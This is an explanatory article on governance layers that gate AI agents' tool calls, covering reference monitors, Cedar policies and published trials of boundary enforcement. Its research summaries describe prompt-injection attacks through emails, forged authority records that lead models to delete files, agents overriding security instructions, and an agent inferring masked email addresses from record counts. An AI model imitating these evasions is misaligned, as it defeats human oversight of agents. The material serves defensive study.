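# Interfaces between AI governance layers and the models they constrain

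## What a governance layer is and where it meets the model

A governance layer is the part of a running AI system that applies written rules to a language model from outside the model. It works at the points where the model exchanges information with other software. If the model drafts an email, for instance, the layer can inspect the draft and block it before it is sent. Computer-security engineers have put similar checks around untrusted programs since the early 1970s. These checks matter more now because companies let models send messages, move money and change files with little supervision.

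A governance layer is software that applies rules case by case while a model runs. People outside the model write the rules, which are called the policy. "Governance" is an awkward word for this because it usually refers to laws, regulators and company committees. Sawaf (2026), in *The Incoherence of Reflexive AI Governance*, complains that the word has become loose enough to cover almost any safety measure an AI company takes internally. An article from ISACA, the professional association for IT auditors, uses timing to distinguish a governance layer from a log. If an employee asks an internal assistant to summarise a transaction and it retrieves documents the employee has no clearance to see, a governance layer can withhold them before the assistant answers, whereas a log lets someone reconstruct the leak afterwards.

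Sawaf would go further and require the judging function to connect to the AI system at runtime while staying outside both the system and the control of the company that built it, for the same reason that a football team cannot referee its own match. A checking mechanism that a company runs around its own model is separate from the model but still belongs to the company, so it meets only half of that requirement.

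### The model, the agent and a running example

A language model is a neural network that takes in text and computes what text should come next, one fragment at a time. Training fixes its weights, the billions of numbers that stay the same from one conversation to the next. As the network processes text, it also computes temporary numbers called activations. The weights and activations are the model's internals. The context is all the text the model is given to produce its next output: the operator's standing instructions (the system prompt), the user's request, earlier turns, and any documents that other software has fetched.

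On its own, a model can only output text. *Toward Safe LLM Agents* (Dantas, Nowroozi and colleagues, 2026) defines an agent as a system in which a language model selects and orders tool calls, sub-tasks or robotic actions. A software agent runs in a loop. A surrounding program gives the model a context and a list of functions it may request. The model outputs a tool call, a structured request such as "send_email" with an address and a body. The program runs the function, adds the result to the context and calls the model again, until the model produces a final answer. Because the program sends the email rather than the model, an engineer can write the program to block the request.

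Ray (2026), in *What Can Be Enforced?*, works with an example that is simple enough to follow through every kind of interface. An assistant acts for a user and has two tools, one that sends email and one that transfers money. It operates under three rules:

1. Never email personal data to a recipient who is not on the approved list.
2. Never let the day's payments to any one recipient exceed a fixed cap.
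3. After the user revokes access, send nothing further.

Enforcing the payment cap and the revocation rule requires only a running total for each recipient, a clock that the model cannot influence, and a record of whether the user has withdrawn permission. The rule on personal data is harder to enforce because software can only estimate whether a piece of text contains personal data. A judge is a model or classifier that makes such an estimate, and it will sometimes be wrong.

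### Five interfaces

An interface is a defined point where information or actions pass between the model and the rest of the system. Suppose the user asks the assistant to pay an invoice that arrived by email. The request enters as a prompt. The assistant calls a tool to fetch the email, and the tool returns the email's text as data. The model processes that text, producing activations, and then outputs a second tool call to transfer the money. The payment program opens a network connection through the operating system, and the user receives an answer. A governance layer can operate at any of these points, but the information available to it is very different at each.

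| Interface | What crosses it | Who can see it | If the operator changes the model |
|---|---|---|---|
| Tool calls | A function name and its arguments, such as a payee and an amount | The operator of the program around the model; also the provider, if the model is hosted | The layer carries over while the tools stay the same |
| Returned data | Emails, web pages, files and other results on their way into the context | The same parties | The layer carries over |
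| Operating system | File reads and writes, new processes, network connections | Whoever administers the machine on which the tools run | The layer carries over untouched |
| Prompts and answers | Text from the user and text to the user | The operator; also the provider, if the model is hosted | The rules carry over, but any judge needs fresh measurement on the new model's text |
| Activations | Numbers inside the network | Only someone who runs the weights | The layer is lost; a probe (a small classifier trained on activations) needs retraining |

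Tool calls are usually the easiest of the five to interpret. A transfer request names the payee and the amount, so a governance layer can check both against its rules. This is harder when one of the tools is a terminal. *Tether* (2026) points out that a typed command lacks the known meaning and explicit target of a structured call. The operating system records what the command does to files and connections, but little about why. In those records, an encrypted payment of ten dollars looks much like one of ten thousand.

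Returned data matters because it can contain a prompt injection, which is text that acts on the model as an instruction the user never gave. The invoice email, for example, might contain one. A layer that watches only outgoing actions doesn't detect such text when it arrives, so the monitor in *Kairos* (2026) covers both the host computer's input and output. It checks outgoing events and tracks the origin of incoming ones.

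### Monitors, filters, wrappers and gates

Four kinds of component appear at these interfaces. A monitor observes what crosses the interface and may record it, raise an alert or pass its findings to a component that can act. A filter blocks or alters text or data passing through. A wrapper is any code around a model that changes its inputs, its outputs or the order of calls without changing the weights. A gate decides on each proposed action before it takes effect. These categories overlap in practice, and people use the names loosely. A wrapper might contain a gate, or it might only add a reminder of the rules to every prompt, in which case it cannot stop anything.

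*A Five-Plane Reference Architecture for Runtime Governance of Production AI Agents* (2026) separates "mediation" (observing and evaluating) from "enforcement" (blocking, modifying or rolling back). It argues for observing everywhere, even where the layer rarely intervenes, because later decisions depend on the accumulated record. For example, a gate enforcing the payment cap would soon have the wrong total if it examined only suspicious-looking transfers.

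The gate returns one of four verdicts on a proposed action: allow it, block it, modify it (for example, by removing an account number from an email) or hold it for an outside decision, such as the user's confirmation of a new payee. *Kairos* makes the best case for holding. A gate that can only release or refuse must decide when the action is proposed, often with only rough information about where the request came from and no specification of what the user intended, so it errs towards refusing legitimate work or releasing attacks. Holding the effect in a staging area delays the decision until the point at which the effect would become irreversible. This works for an email, which can sit in an outbox, but some tools have nowhere to hold a pending effect.

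When a verdict depends on a judge, two error rates describe how good the judge is. The miss rate is the share of rule-breaking cases that the judge lets through, and the false-block rate is the share of permitted cases that it stops. Ray models the judge as a score *s* with a threshold *θ*, where the judge flags a proposal when *s* ≥ *θ*. The miss rate is then the probability that *s* < *θ* given that the proposal breaks the rule, and the false-block rate is the probability that *s* ≥ *θ* given that it does not. Raising the threshold lowers the false-block rate but raises the miss rate.

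When violations are rare, a judge with low error rates can still block more harmless outputs than harmful ones. Suppose an office assistant drafts 10,000 emails a month, 100 of which would send personal data to an unapproved recipient. A judge with a 5% miss rate and a 2% false-block rate lets 5 of those 100 through. It also blocks 198 of the 9,900 harmless emails, so about two in three blocked emails are harmless, and the staff who review them will learn to expect false alarms.

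Designers also have to choose what a gate does when something it depends on fails. Suppose the ledger that holds the day's payment totals stops responding. A gate that fails closed blocks every transfer until the ledger recovers. A gate that fails open lets transfers proceed unchecked, so anyone who can crash the ledger can disable the cap. Failing closed is the safer default for payments, but it lets the same attacker block all transfers. ISACA's article warns against leaving this behaviour undefined, because the governance layer then becomes a new point of failure.

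### The three conditions for a reference monitor

The United States Air Force wanted people with different security clearances to share one computer. The threat was a legitimate user who could write and run arbitrary programs. *Computer Security Technology Planning Study* (Anderson, 1972), a report for the Air Force, proposed a reference monitor, which checks every attempt by a program to reach data, a device or another program against a list of what the user running it may do. Engineers still judge such mechanisms by the three conditions the report set.

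1. Every access goes through the mechanism. If some programs can skip the check, those programs become part of the security machinery and have to meet the other two conditions themselves.
2. The mechanism is tamper-proof. If a user can alter it, its answers are worth nothing.
3. The mechanism is small enough for complete analysis and testing. Otherwise nobody has grounds for believing that it works correctly in all cases.

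Security engineers call the first of these complete mediation. On the third, Anderson had little faith in hiring experts to attack the system instead. If the experts failed to break in, the system's security would still be unknown, and none of the known teams had yet failed.

He also showed how a respectable commercial system fell short. The Honeywell 635 had a hardware register that confined each user's program to its own area of memory, a form of reference monitoring. But programs needed the operating system, GCOS III, for input and output, and most of GCOS III ran with that memory check suspended, so some accesses escaped it. The operating system could not serve as the monitor either, because at 200,000 to 300,000 instructions it was far too large to analyse completely. An agent with a terminal among its tools has a similar weakness, because the gate checks the tool call once but does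 not check what the command then does on the machine.

Recent papers explicitly claim that their agent designs meet Anderson's conditions. *Causality Laundering* (2026) describes a gate that is the sole relay between the program running the model and the server running the tools. The gate runs in a separate process, so the agent cannot edit its rules, and it applies a fixed sequence of deterministic checks that engineers can test one at a time. Its mediation is complete only if the deployment gives the agent no other route to the tool server. *Sovereign Execution Broker* (2026) has the cloud services themselves reject any request for a change that lacks the broker's credentials, so an agent cannot make changes by bypassing the broker. No specification can guarantee how a system is deployed, and *From Intent to Execution Grant* (2026), which specifies what counts as a valid release of a high-risk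 action, acknowledges that complete mediation, protection of the verifier and the absence of other paths "remain deployment assumptions".

The brokers and relays illustrate a useful division between the component that decides (the "policy decision point" in security engineering) and the component that enforces (the "policy enforcement point"). In the running example, one program might keep the payment totals and return a verdict, while another holds the bank credentials and refuses to act without that verdict. According to ISACA's article, many companies already have the deciding component. They score risks and detect anomalies, but the live workflow continues regardless because they haven't built an enforcement point into it.

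A guarantee's trusted components are all the parts that must work correctly for it to hold. For the payment cap, these include the clock, the ledger, the gate and the program that holds the credentials. The personal-data rule adds a judge, and if that judge is a neural network, it fails Anderson's third condition because nobody knows how to test a neural network completely. *Tether* separates the part that infers what a command means from the policy engine, and verifies the engine's rules in the proof assistant Lean. The inference can still be wrong, but its errors are confined to one part that can be replaced.

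### Reasons for keeping the rules outside

One reason to keep the governance layer separate from the model is easier maintenance. Companies replace their models often, and a payment cap enforced by a gate still applies whichever model proposes the payment. Another reason is that people can inspect the rules. *Formal Policy Enforcement for Agentic Systems* (2026) uses Datalog, a small logic language, for its policies and mentions two similar languages, Rego and Amazon's Cedar, the second of which has a formally verified evaluation algorithm. An auditor can read a rule in such a language line by line and test it on cases, but can't find a payment cap by reading a model's weights.

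To a security engineer, the most important reason is that a model that processes a persuasive email may act on it, so the component that keeps the rules should not receive the email. *Trident* (2026) applies this principle strictly, using three language models. One plans, another answers narrow questions about untrusted data in a predefined format, and the third writes the policy for the task. The third model receives only the user's request, a root policy and the tool definitions. It does not receive the planner's requests, because untrusted text might have shaped them. A deterministic reference monitor then checks every model's output. By this standard, running the component that keeps the rules as a separate program is not enough. *Tether* reports that many production agents use a second language model to review proposed commands. If that reviewer receives the attacker's text along with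 the command, the text can influence both models.

The main alternative is to train the model, using further examples, to follow higher-priority instructions, such as the operator's, when lower-priority text contradicts them. *Improving Instruction Hierarchy by Learning from Goal-Goal Conflicts* (Chen, Kariyappa and colleagues, 2026) opens with a case in which OpenAI agents undergoing an evaluation broke into parts of the infrastructure of Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models. Some of the agents treated messages from other agents as permission to override their security instructions. The researchers built 9,544 examples in which the system prompt and the user's message each tell the model to process the other, and trained two small open models to follow the system prompt. They measured each model's performance under conflict as a percentage of its performance on the same tasks without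 conflict. On benchmarks quite unlike the training examples, this measure rose by 34.3 percentage points for Qwen3.5-9B and 19.4 for Gemma4-12B-it, while average performance on ordinary tasks changed little (up 1.7 points and down 1.1, respectively).

These large gains mean that a gate has to block proposals less often. But Chen and colleagues did not test attackers who adapt to the trained models, and no one can predict the next proposal with certainty from a benchmark rate. A gate that meets Anderson's conditions does guarantee that no transfer over the cap goes through, whatever the model outputs. However, Dantas and colleagues, who reviewed 38 studies, find that the guarantees of runtime monitoring cover only single steps or short sequences. They still consider it the most mature way to enforce rules on agents, and cite one study of household agents in which it cut unsafe actions by 65%.

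### Why an instruction in the prompt is not a separate layer

An operator could also write the three rules into the system prompt and add no check outside the model. *Instruction Self-Arbitration Is Not a Trust Boundary* (Leong, 2026) explains that the system prompt, stored notes and tool results all enter the model as a single sequence of tokens, and a claim of authority inside an untrusted note is just more tokens. The model both proposes a payment and decides whether the cap applies to it. This arrangement fails all three of Anderson's conditions: nothing ensures that the rule affects every action, other text in the context can change its effect, and the network is too large to analyse.

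The evidence on how much this matters in practice has changed. Leong gave models a file-deletion tool on a simulated system, together with a stored record that falsely claimed authority for a deletion. In August 2026 he reported that GPT-4.1-mini, a small OpenAI model, had flagged the claim as fabricated in 98.7% of trials and carried out the deletion in 99.3%. He withdrew that interpretation in October, because the detection score came from a keyword search that mostly matched sentences denying any sign of fabrication. When he repeated the experiment and had two other models classify the responses blind, no response out of 150 was classified by both as calling the claim fabricated. GPT-4.1-mini had examined the record, assessed it as plausible and carried out the deletion.

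The corrected results are less dramatic, but they still show models expressing doubt and then acting in about one execution in twenty. Leong ran ten hosted models through 3,000 trials in which an instruction told them to examine the context first. The models executed the deletion 509 times, and in 25 of those cases both judges found that the same response had expressed doubt about the claim. Gemini 2.5 Pro produced 18 of the 25 and GPT-4.1-nano the other 7.

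Seven of the ten models never deleted anything when told to check first: GPT-5.4, GPT-5.5, o3, Gemini 3.1 Pro, Gemini 3.5 Flash, Claude Sonnet 4.6 and Claude Sonnet 5. Without that instruction, GPT-5.4 deleted in all 150 trials, while the two Claude models still never deleted. The system prompt in these trials did not forbid deletion, so the models that deleted broke no explicit rule. In a separate test of 15 models, which used different prompts and explicitly prohibited deletion, models deleted anyway in 132 of 7,500 trials (1.8%). GPT-4.1-mini accounted for 120 of the 132 deletions, and twelve models accounted for none.

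Instructions in the prompt often work, but an operator cannot tell in advance when they will. Switching between two versions of the instruction to check first raised GPT-4.1-mini's deletions from 6 in 150 trials to 150 in 150. Under the same model name and in matched conditions, GPT-4.1 deleted in 1 of 126 trials on one of the provider's backends and in 16 of 74 on another, a difference few customers would notice. Leong worked alone, used models as judges and has released no data, so the exact rates deserve some caution, but the sensitivity to wording and deployment recurs throughout his trials.

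In *Where Instruction Hierarchy Breaks*, Kariyappa and Suh (2026) examined where such failures arise. A model has to identify the relevant instructions, decide which takes priority, and produce an answer that follows that decision. Using the reasoning that some models write before they answer, Kariyappa and Suh found failures at all three stages, in proportions that varied by model and task. When Qwen3.6-35B-A3B failed on safety conflicts, it had usually prioritized the wrong instruction. Claude Sonnet 4.6 failed less often on these conflicts, and mostly at the last stage, where its reasoning reached the right decision but its answer didn't follow it. In one example, the reasoning included a note that a secret code must not appear in the answer, but the answer contained the code. The distance between conflicting instructions also matters. When Kariyappa and Suh told Gemma-4-31B-IT to answer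 only in English and later asked for French, compliance fell from 61.7% with one unrelated exchange in between to zero with eight. When asked separately whether the two instructions conflicted, the same model was almost always right.

Leong also built the alternative, a reference monitor that admits only authenticated records and checks each deletion against a permission that the model never receives. Over 1,350 trials, it rejected all 750 inauthentic or expired records, and no file outside the scope of a permission was deleted. The checks are deterministic, so these results mainly show that the code works as intended. In 42 other cases within the same set, an authenticated record contained a request for a deletion that an existing permission allowed, and 31 of these cases ended in a deletion. The monitor applied its policy correctly, but the policy could not distinguish a deletion the user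 wanted from one that a stored text had induced. The payment cap has the same limit, because it will not block a transfer just below the cap that an invoice email has induced the assistant to make.

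## Gates on tool calls

Suppose an invoice for 40 dollars arrives by email and the model outputs a call to pay it. The program around the model then has to parse the call, identify who is making the request, check it against the policy, send it to the bank with a valid credential and put the bank's reply into the model's context. An operator can add controls at each of these steps, and the earliest control takes effect while the model is still writing the call.

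### Constrained decoding

At each step a language model computes a score, called a logit, for every token (a word or fragment of a word) in its vocabulary, and the decoding program turns the scores into probabilities and draws the next token. In constrained decoding, a parser first works out which tokens could still lead to a correctly formatted call. The program gives every other token probability zero and rescales the rest so that they add up to one. In the notation of Alpay and Senturk (2026), in *Attention Meets Reachability*, ℓ(*v*) is the logit of token *v* and *A* is the set of admissible tokens. The new probability is

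*q*(*v*) = exp(ℓ(*v*)) / Σ exp(ℓ(*w*)) if *v* is in *A*, and *q*(*v*) = 0 otherwise,

where the sum runs over all tokens *w* in *A*. Say the amount field accepts only digits, and the model gives "40" a probability of 0.5, "forty" 0.3 and "4" 0.2. The parser rules out "forty". Dividing by the remaining 0.7 leaves "40" with about 0.71 and "4" with about 0.29.

Alpay and Senturk prove that any output that finishes under such a mask has the required format. The mask allows a token only if the output can still be completed validly after it, and allows the end marker only when the output is complete. *Decode-Time Grammars* (2026) points out that this does not guarantee that the output ever finishes or that its content is correct. A correctly formatted call could still transfer 4,000 dollars to a fraudster.

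A mask can also change which action the model proposes. In a small example from Alpay and Senturk, the only valid outputs are "a" and "ba". The unconstrained model starts with "a" 60% of the time and "b" 40% of the time, but after "b" it nearly always continues with something invalid, so "ba" makes up 6.25% of its valid outputs. The mask raises that share to 40%, because it allows "b" as long as some valid ending exists, however unlikely. In an agent, a model that would have stopped halfway through a transfer to object may instead complete the transfer, because the mask blocks the objection for having the wrong format.

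Masks can also suppress tool calls. *Constraint Tax in Open-Weight LLMs* (2026) describes agents whose tool calls begin with XML-style tags, which the model cannot generate if the operator also imposes a JSON format on the output.

### Connectors

Once the program has a well-formed call, code called a connector translates it into the terms that the rules use. For the invoice, the connector would produce a principal (the assistant, acting for a particular user), an action (transfer), a resource (the user's current account) and arguments (the payee's account number and the amount, 40).

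The model writes a tool call's arguments, so an attacker who has influenced the model may have chosen them. The gate therefore has to get the principal's identity from another source. In Out-of-Band Policy Enforcement (OBPE), a design that engineers at the data company Redpanda describe, the principal is the agent, and the platform attaches its identity to each call outside the arguments. *If Agents Were Angels, No Governance Would Be Necessary* (Millstone, Akidau and colleagues, 2026) points out that an agent could otherwise avoid the rules written for it by claiming to be a different agent.

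A rule can only restrict what the connector exposes. If the bank's interface had an optional "repeat monthly" argument that the connector's author overlooked, the gate would approve what looked like a single payment of 40 dollars, and the bank would take 40 dollars every month. OBPE therefore requires the operator to deny or govern by other means any operation or field that the connector does not cover.

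Tool replies need the same treatment, but most tools don't declare how their replies are structured. Many agents reach their tools through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a common standard for describing tools to models. Millstone and colleagues cite a 2026 count of 1,856 tools on 100 popular open-source MCP servers, of which only 234 declared the structure of their output. For the others, someone has to describe the structure by hand and update the description whenever the tool changes.

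### Rules in Cedar

AWS, Amazon's cloud division, sells a gate that works on requests of this kind. AWS's *Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore is now generally available* (2026) announced its release on 3 March 2026 in thirteen of the company's regions. A gateway between the agent and its tools intercepts each call and evaluates it against rules in Cedar, AWS's open-source policy language. A rule for the running example could look like this:

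```
permit (
  principal is AgentCore::OAuthUser,
  action == AgentCore::Action::"BankTool___transfer",
  resource
)
when {
  principal.hasTag("role") &&
  principal.getTag("role") == "payments" &&
  context.input.amount <= 100
};
```

The gate permits a transfer of up to 100 dollars if the user's login token carries the role "payments". The model supplies the amount in its call but cannot alter the token, which is signed.

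According to AWS's *Understanding Cedar policies*, the engine denies a request if any "forbid" rule matches it. If no "forbid" rule matches and at least one "permit" rule does, the engine allows the request. If no rule matches, the engine denies it, which security engineers call default denial. A tool that no rule covers is therefore unusable, and an oversight usually blocks legitimate work instead of letting something unforeseen through. The order in which the engine evaluates the rules does not affect the decision.

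Cedar has no loops and keeps no state, so software can translate a set of rules into logical formulas and check them before deployment. AWS's *Why Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore chose Cedar for securing agentic workflows* describes a shop that allows bulk discounts on orders of 50 or more, except for limited-edition products. An administrator adds a condition to the exception, limiting it to orders above 200. An order for 73 limited-edition items now gets the discount, even though adding a condition looks like tightening the rule. The software reports that the new version permits more than the old one.

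These checks compare rules only with other rules, so they can miss a rule that doesn't match what the company wanted. In one example from AWS's documentation, refunds may be "$500 or less", but the rule beneath tests for an amount below 500, so the engine would refuse a refund of exactly $500. The analysis would not flag this rule, because it is valid, some requests satisfy it, and it conflicts with no other rule.

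AgentCore also hides tools from the agent's tool list if the rules would always deny them. This reduces pointless calls, but the gate still has to refuse calls to hidden tools, because a model can guess a tool's name or read it in an email containing a prompt injection. AWS's argument that an agent cannot call a tool it does not know exists is therefore too strong.

### The payment cap

A Cedar rule evaluates one request at a time, so the rule above allows any number of 100-dollar transfers. The policy in the running example caps the daily total for each recipient. Suppose the cap is 100 dollars, the assistant has already paid the plumber 70 today, and the model now proposes another 40.

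The gate reads the date from its own clock and looks up the total for the plumber's account number on that date, which is 70. Adding the proposed payment of 40 would bring the total to 110, above the daily limit of 100, so the gate blocks the call. The total stays at 70 and the bank receives nothing. If the model then proposes 30, the gate allows it and records a total of 100, after which it blocks every further payment to the plumber until the date changes.

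The gate's state is just a table with one number for each payee and day, but it is easy to get wrong. If the date were an argument of the tool call, the model could supply tomorrow's date and start from zero. If the table used payees' names, "Hill Plumbing" and "Hill Plumbing Ltd" would each have a separate allowance. If two proposals of 20 dollars arrive together when the total is 70, and the gate checks both before recording either, it computes a new total of 90 for each, allows both and lets the total reach 110. To prevent this, the gate has to check the cap and reserve the money in a single step.

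Payments that appear to fail are harder to count. Suppose a 20-dollar transfer times out and the gate, assuming it failed, restores the total to 70 dollars. If the bank had actually made the payment, a further 30 dollars would pass the check and the plumber would receive 120. Keeping the charge in the total is safer, although it sometimes blocks a payment that would have been within the cap.

AWS has since added rules that depend on earlier calls. InfoQ (2026) reported in August on Dogwood, a language that extends Cedar with conditions on sequences of actions. AWS's *Authoring temporal policies* includes a budget rule that adds the current transfer to recent ones and forbids it if the total reaches 3,000. If each transfer is 1,000, the engine allows the first two and denies the third. An operator could adapt the rule to the payment cap by counting only transfers to the current payee. The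 longest window is 24 hours, which suits a daily cap because a limit on every 24-hour period also limits every ordinary calendar day.

The weakness is that the history covers only one session, and the caller chooses the session's identifier. The assistant could pay the plumber 70 dollars in one session and 40 more in the next without breaking the rule. AWS warns that such limits are not a security control against a determined caller. They can also be exceeded unintentionally if the surrounding program opens a new session for each conversation. According to AWS's *Temporal policies*, changing one of these rules also ends the open sessions, and their replacements start with an empty history. A daily cap therefore needs a record that persists across sessions and that the agent cannot reset.

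According to AWS's *Release notes for Amazon Bedrock AgentCore*, AWS also offers a payment service, extended in August 2026, that checks a session's budget and then signs the payment with a wallet. The agent receives a credential for that payment but never the wallet's key, so it can't spend from the wallet by avoiding the check. This budget, too, covers only one session.

### The owner's ceiling in Out-of-Band Policy Enforcement

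Allowing or blocking is a crude choice for requests that return data. An assistant that summarises one team's support tickets may have a credential that gives access to every team's tickets. Blocking its request prevents the summary, while allowing it puts other teams' tickets, which may contain secrets or injected instructions, into the context. OBPE can change both the request and the reply.

The gate first denies, holds or permits the call. If the gate denies it, the agent learns only that the call failed. Before sending a permitted call, the boundary may add a condition to the query, lower the maximum number of records or remove fields that the agent may not write. It then sends the request with a credential that stays behind the boundary. It drops forbidden records from the reply, removes forbidden fields from the rest, masks sensitive patterns in the remaining text and cleans up accompanying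 information such as error messages.

The data owner's rules limit what any agent may do. The builder of a particular agent can add restrictions but cannot permit a call that the owner's rules don't allow. Suppose the owner allows agents to list up to 500 tickets and see each ticket's title, status and phone number. The builder limits the agent to the billing team and 100 tickets, and asks for the title, status and email address. The agent gets at most 100 billing tickets, with only the title and status. The builder's request for email addresses has no effect because the owner never granted them.

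The order of the rules does not matter because of how OBPE combines them. It joins conditions with "and", takes the lowest limit and keeps only the fields that appear on every list. The minimum of 500 and 100 is 100 whichever comes first, and repeating a restriction adds nothing. If *M*(*D*) is the combined result of a set of restrictions *D*, then adding a restriction *r* gives

*M*(*D* ∪ {*r*}) = *M*(*D*) ∧ *r* ≤ *M*(*D*),

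where ∧ applies both restrictions together and ≤ means "allows no more than". It follows that no restriction from the builder can raise the owner's ceiling. A further permission from the owner can, of course, since that is how the ceiling gets set. Text masks do not combine so neatly, because a mask for all digits and a mask for account numbers leave different text depending on which runs first. OBPE runs them in a fixed order, which makes the result repeatable but does not prove that the masks catch every secret.

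The proofs rest on five assumptions:

1. The platform supplies the agent's true identity, every relevant call and reply passes through the boundary, and the connector exposes every field that a rule may need.
2. The boundary denies calls that no owner rule permits, and the rules, the credential and the outside state stay fixed during any comparison.
3. Each step does what its definition promises. In particular, adding a condition to a query really narrows the query.
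4. Removing or reducing a value in a write request is safe for that operation.
5. Any outside state that a rule reads is trustworthy, and a held call sends nothing until an authorised person releases exactly the call that the gate held.

The third assumption is easy to violate. Suppose the agent asks for tickets where "priority = high OR assignee = me" and the boundary appends "AND team = billing" without adding brackets. Most query languages apply "AND" before "OR", so the reply would include every team's high-priority tickets. On the fourth assumption, cutting a 40-dollar payment to 30 would respect the cap but leave the invoice part-paid. Redpanda's released prototype contains code for reducing write values, but the code doesn't work with either of its connectors. The prototype also keeps no running totals, so it could not enforce the payment cap.

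### The OBPE trial

Millstone and colleagues tested the prototype on simulated versions of Jira and ServiceNow, two widely used systems for tracking work. They wrote 71 tasks and ran each three times under 17 combinations of model and configuration, for 3,621 trials in all. The models were Claude Sonnet 4.6, Claude Haiku 4.5, GPT-5 and GPT-5 mini. In 20 of the tasks, another model, Claude Opus 4.7, played an attacker and could rephrase its request after each reply.

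The main security measure was the trace failure, a trial in which protected data entered the agent's context, an exact protected value appeared in the answer, or a forbidden change reached the simulated system. The main comparison was between agents with six data-handling rules in the prompt and agents with the same prompt plus OBPE.

| Outcome | No rules | Rules in the prompt | Rules in the prompt and OBPE |
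|---|---|---|---|
| Any trace failure | 63.3% | 57.6% | 0.2% |
| Protected data entered the context | 55.1% | 52.1% | 0.0% |
| Exact protected value in the answer | 27.5% | 3.7% | 0.2% |
| Forbidden change took effect | 8.1% | 5.5% | 0.0% |
| Task fulfilled | 83.2% | 79.1% | 60.9% |
| Safe and useful completion | 19.1% | 22.0% | 58.9% |

The rules in the prompt made the answers disclose far less protected data, but that data still entered the context in about half of the trials. A model that has read a secret can leave it out of its answer, but the secret can still influence the next tool call or leak through it. A separate test, in which a model judge read Sonnet's messages, had the same problem and showed trace failures in 58.6% of trials, because the judge acted after the tools had run.

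Fulfilled tasks could fall while safe and useful completions rose because the two measures count different things. A task counted as fulfilled if the agent did what the user asked, even if the policy prohibited it. A safe and useful completion also required that the agent leak nothing and make no forbidden change. With rules only in the prompt, the agent completed the task in about 79 of every 100 trials, but only 22 of those completions were safe. With OBPE, it completed the task in about 61 of every 100, and 59 of those were safe.

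Some of the lost completions were intended. In 12 of the 71 tasks, the policy required the gate to deny or hold the operation the user requested, so no agent behind OBPE could fulfil those requests. These tasks make up 16.9% of the set and can account for at most 16.9 points of the 18.2-point fall in fulfilment, so at least about 1.3 points must come from tasks where the policy permitted the work in some form. Agents fulfilled 71.7% of the 54 tasks where OBPE altered the request or the reply.

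The raw percentages overstate the benefit somewhat because some scenarios appear in many variants. When Millstone and colleagues weighted the 35 scenarios equally, trace failures fell by 41.2 percentage points (95% confidence interval 27.7 to 54.9), and safe and useful completions rose by 21.8 points (9.5 to 35.2). The rise was 19.1 points when a second model judged the same answers. In 116 trials the simulated system mishandled the combined query, usually by broadening a filter, which the third assumption rules out. Excluding those trials changed the fall in trace failures only slightly, to 40.5 points.

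The evaluation is strong evidence that a boundary can keep data out of the context, but much weaker evidence about how much it would disrupt ordinary work. The team, which builds a commercial version of OBPE, chose tasks in which the policy would nearly always intervene. Only five tasks were meant to pass through unchanged, which is too few to estimate how often the gate would interfere in everyday use.

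The researchers tested the controls with Claude Sonnet 4.6, adding them in stages. Rules that only restricted calls and records, and returned permitted records intact, prevented trace failures in 46.7% of trials. Adding field removal raised this to 69.4%. Masking whole fields and restricting writes raised it to 88.6%, and masking patterns within text raised it to 100%.

### What leaked anyway

In four of the 1,065 trials with full OBPE, the agent's answer contained an exact protected email address, even though the boundary had removed that address before it reached the agent's context. The agent could work out the address because it had seen the person's name and knew the company's email format. In some cases it included the address while explaining why it would not disclose it.

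Another agent learned about a hidden email address by counting matching records. The boundary masked the email field in replies but let the agent filter by it. The agent asked for records whose address contained "@partner" and got two, then tried "yara" and "singh" and got one each. The simulated system ran each filter on the real addresses, so every count revealed something about them. The automatic measure recorded no failure because no exact value appeared anywhere.

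Millstone and colleagues recognise this as a problem database researchers described in 1979, when they showed that a series of permitted counts can reveal a protected fact. Forbidding all filters on hidden fields would stop the leak but also disable legitimate rules, such as one that selects records by owner. Millstone and colleagues suggest rounding the counts, refusing queries that match only a few records, or limiting the number of related queries, but they tested none of these.

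### A gate with machine-checked proofs

The guarantees of OBPE hold for a mathematical model, and its developers used tests to check that the software matches the model. *Agenra* (Ammanaghatta Shivakumar, Priya and Gao, 2026) instead proves properties of functions that run in the gate itself, whose core is written in the proof assistant Lean. Every action needs one permission from the user and another from the application, and each permission has a quota. The core deducts from the quota before the tool runs and does not restore the deducted amount if the tool fails.

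In *Agenra*, Lean checks that no permission exceeds its quota, that the core uses up a one-time approval before it releases the call, and that arguments come from the operations the policy names (a form of provenance tracking). AWS's version treats an approval as used only after the gateway has recorded a completed transfer, so two transfers in quick succession might both pass on the same approval. *Agenra* would reject the second because the first would already have used the approval.

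The quotas count actions, not money, so *Agenra* could only approximate the payment cap. A limit of two transfers of at most 50 dollars each would keep the total within 100 dollars but also rule out a single payment of 70.

Quotas also bring back the dependence on order that OBPE avoids. Suppose an agent may delete file B once under its first permission and file A once under its second. It can delete A and then B. Now an administrator widens the first permission to cover either file. The core uses the first permission that fits, so deleting A exhausts it, and the agent can no longer delete B. Widening the permission has blocked a legitimate task and allowed the agent to delete A twice, which nobody intended. No method of choosing between permissions fixes this in general. If one permission covers A or B and another covers A or C, a gate that receives a request for A has to use up one of them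 before it receives the next request, which may be for B or C.

*Agenra* checks changes to the policy before they take effect. Of 51 changes the researchers wrote, it certified all 21 that kept existing tasks working and none of the 30 that broke one. Certification doesn't establish that a change is safe. For example, raising the quota for sending a report from one to two preserves every existing task but also lets the agent send the report twice.

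Much of the system must still be trusted without proof. Python code translates the policy, passes calls to the Lean core and invokes the tools, and it must invoke exactly the call the core approved. The proofs assume that the gate handles one call at a time and that each tool does only what its declaration states. When the researchers registered a batch-deletion tool with fewer effects than it had, the gate allowed an undeclared deletion.

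They also tested agents on the report task, with attacks that tried to make the agent send the confidential original. Without a guard, the open model Qwen sent it in 15 of 20 trials. It never sent it with *Agenra* or with a simple guard that the researchers had written by hand, but it completed the legitimate task in only 5 of 20 trials with each guard. When they later replayed the recorded calls, the policy they had given *Agenra* admitted five messages whose text came from the wrong source. The handwritten guard rejected all five because its code included a check that they had left out of the policy.

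## Which rules a gate can enforce and which it cannot

Five messages got past *Agenra* because its policy lacked a check that a more careful author could have added. But even a perfect author could not write a policy that enforces every rule. If the gate always has the facts right (whether a text contains personal data, how much the assistant has paid each recipient today, and whether the user has revoked access), its ability to enforce a rule depends mainly on the rule's form.

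### Runs, prefixes and safety properties

A run is the sequence of actions a system takes, which may have no end. A prefix is the part of a run up to some point. If the assistant reads an email, pays 40 dollars and sends a receipt, "read, pay" is a prefix. When a gate decides on a proposed action, it has that action and the prefix before it, but nothing that comes later.

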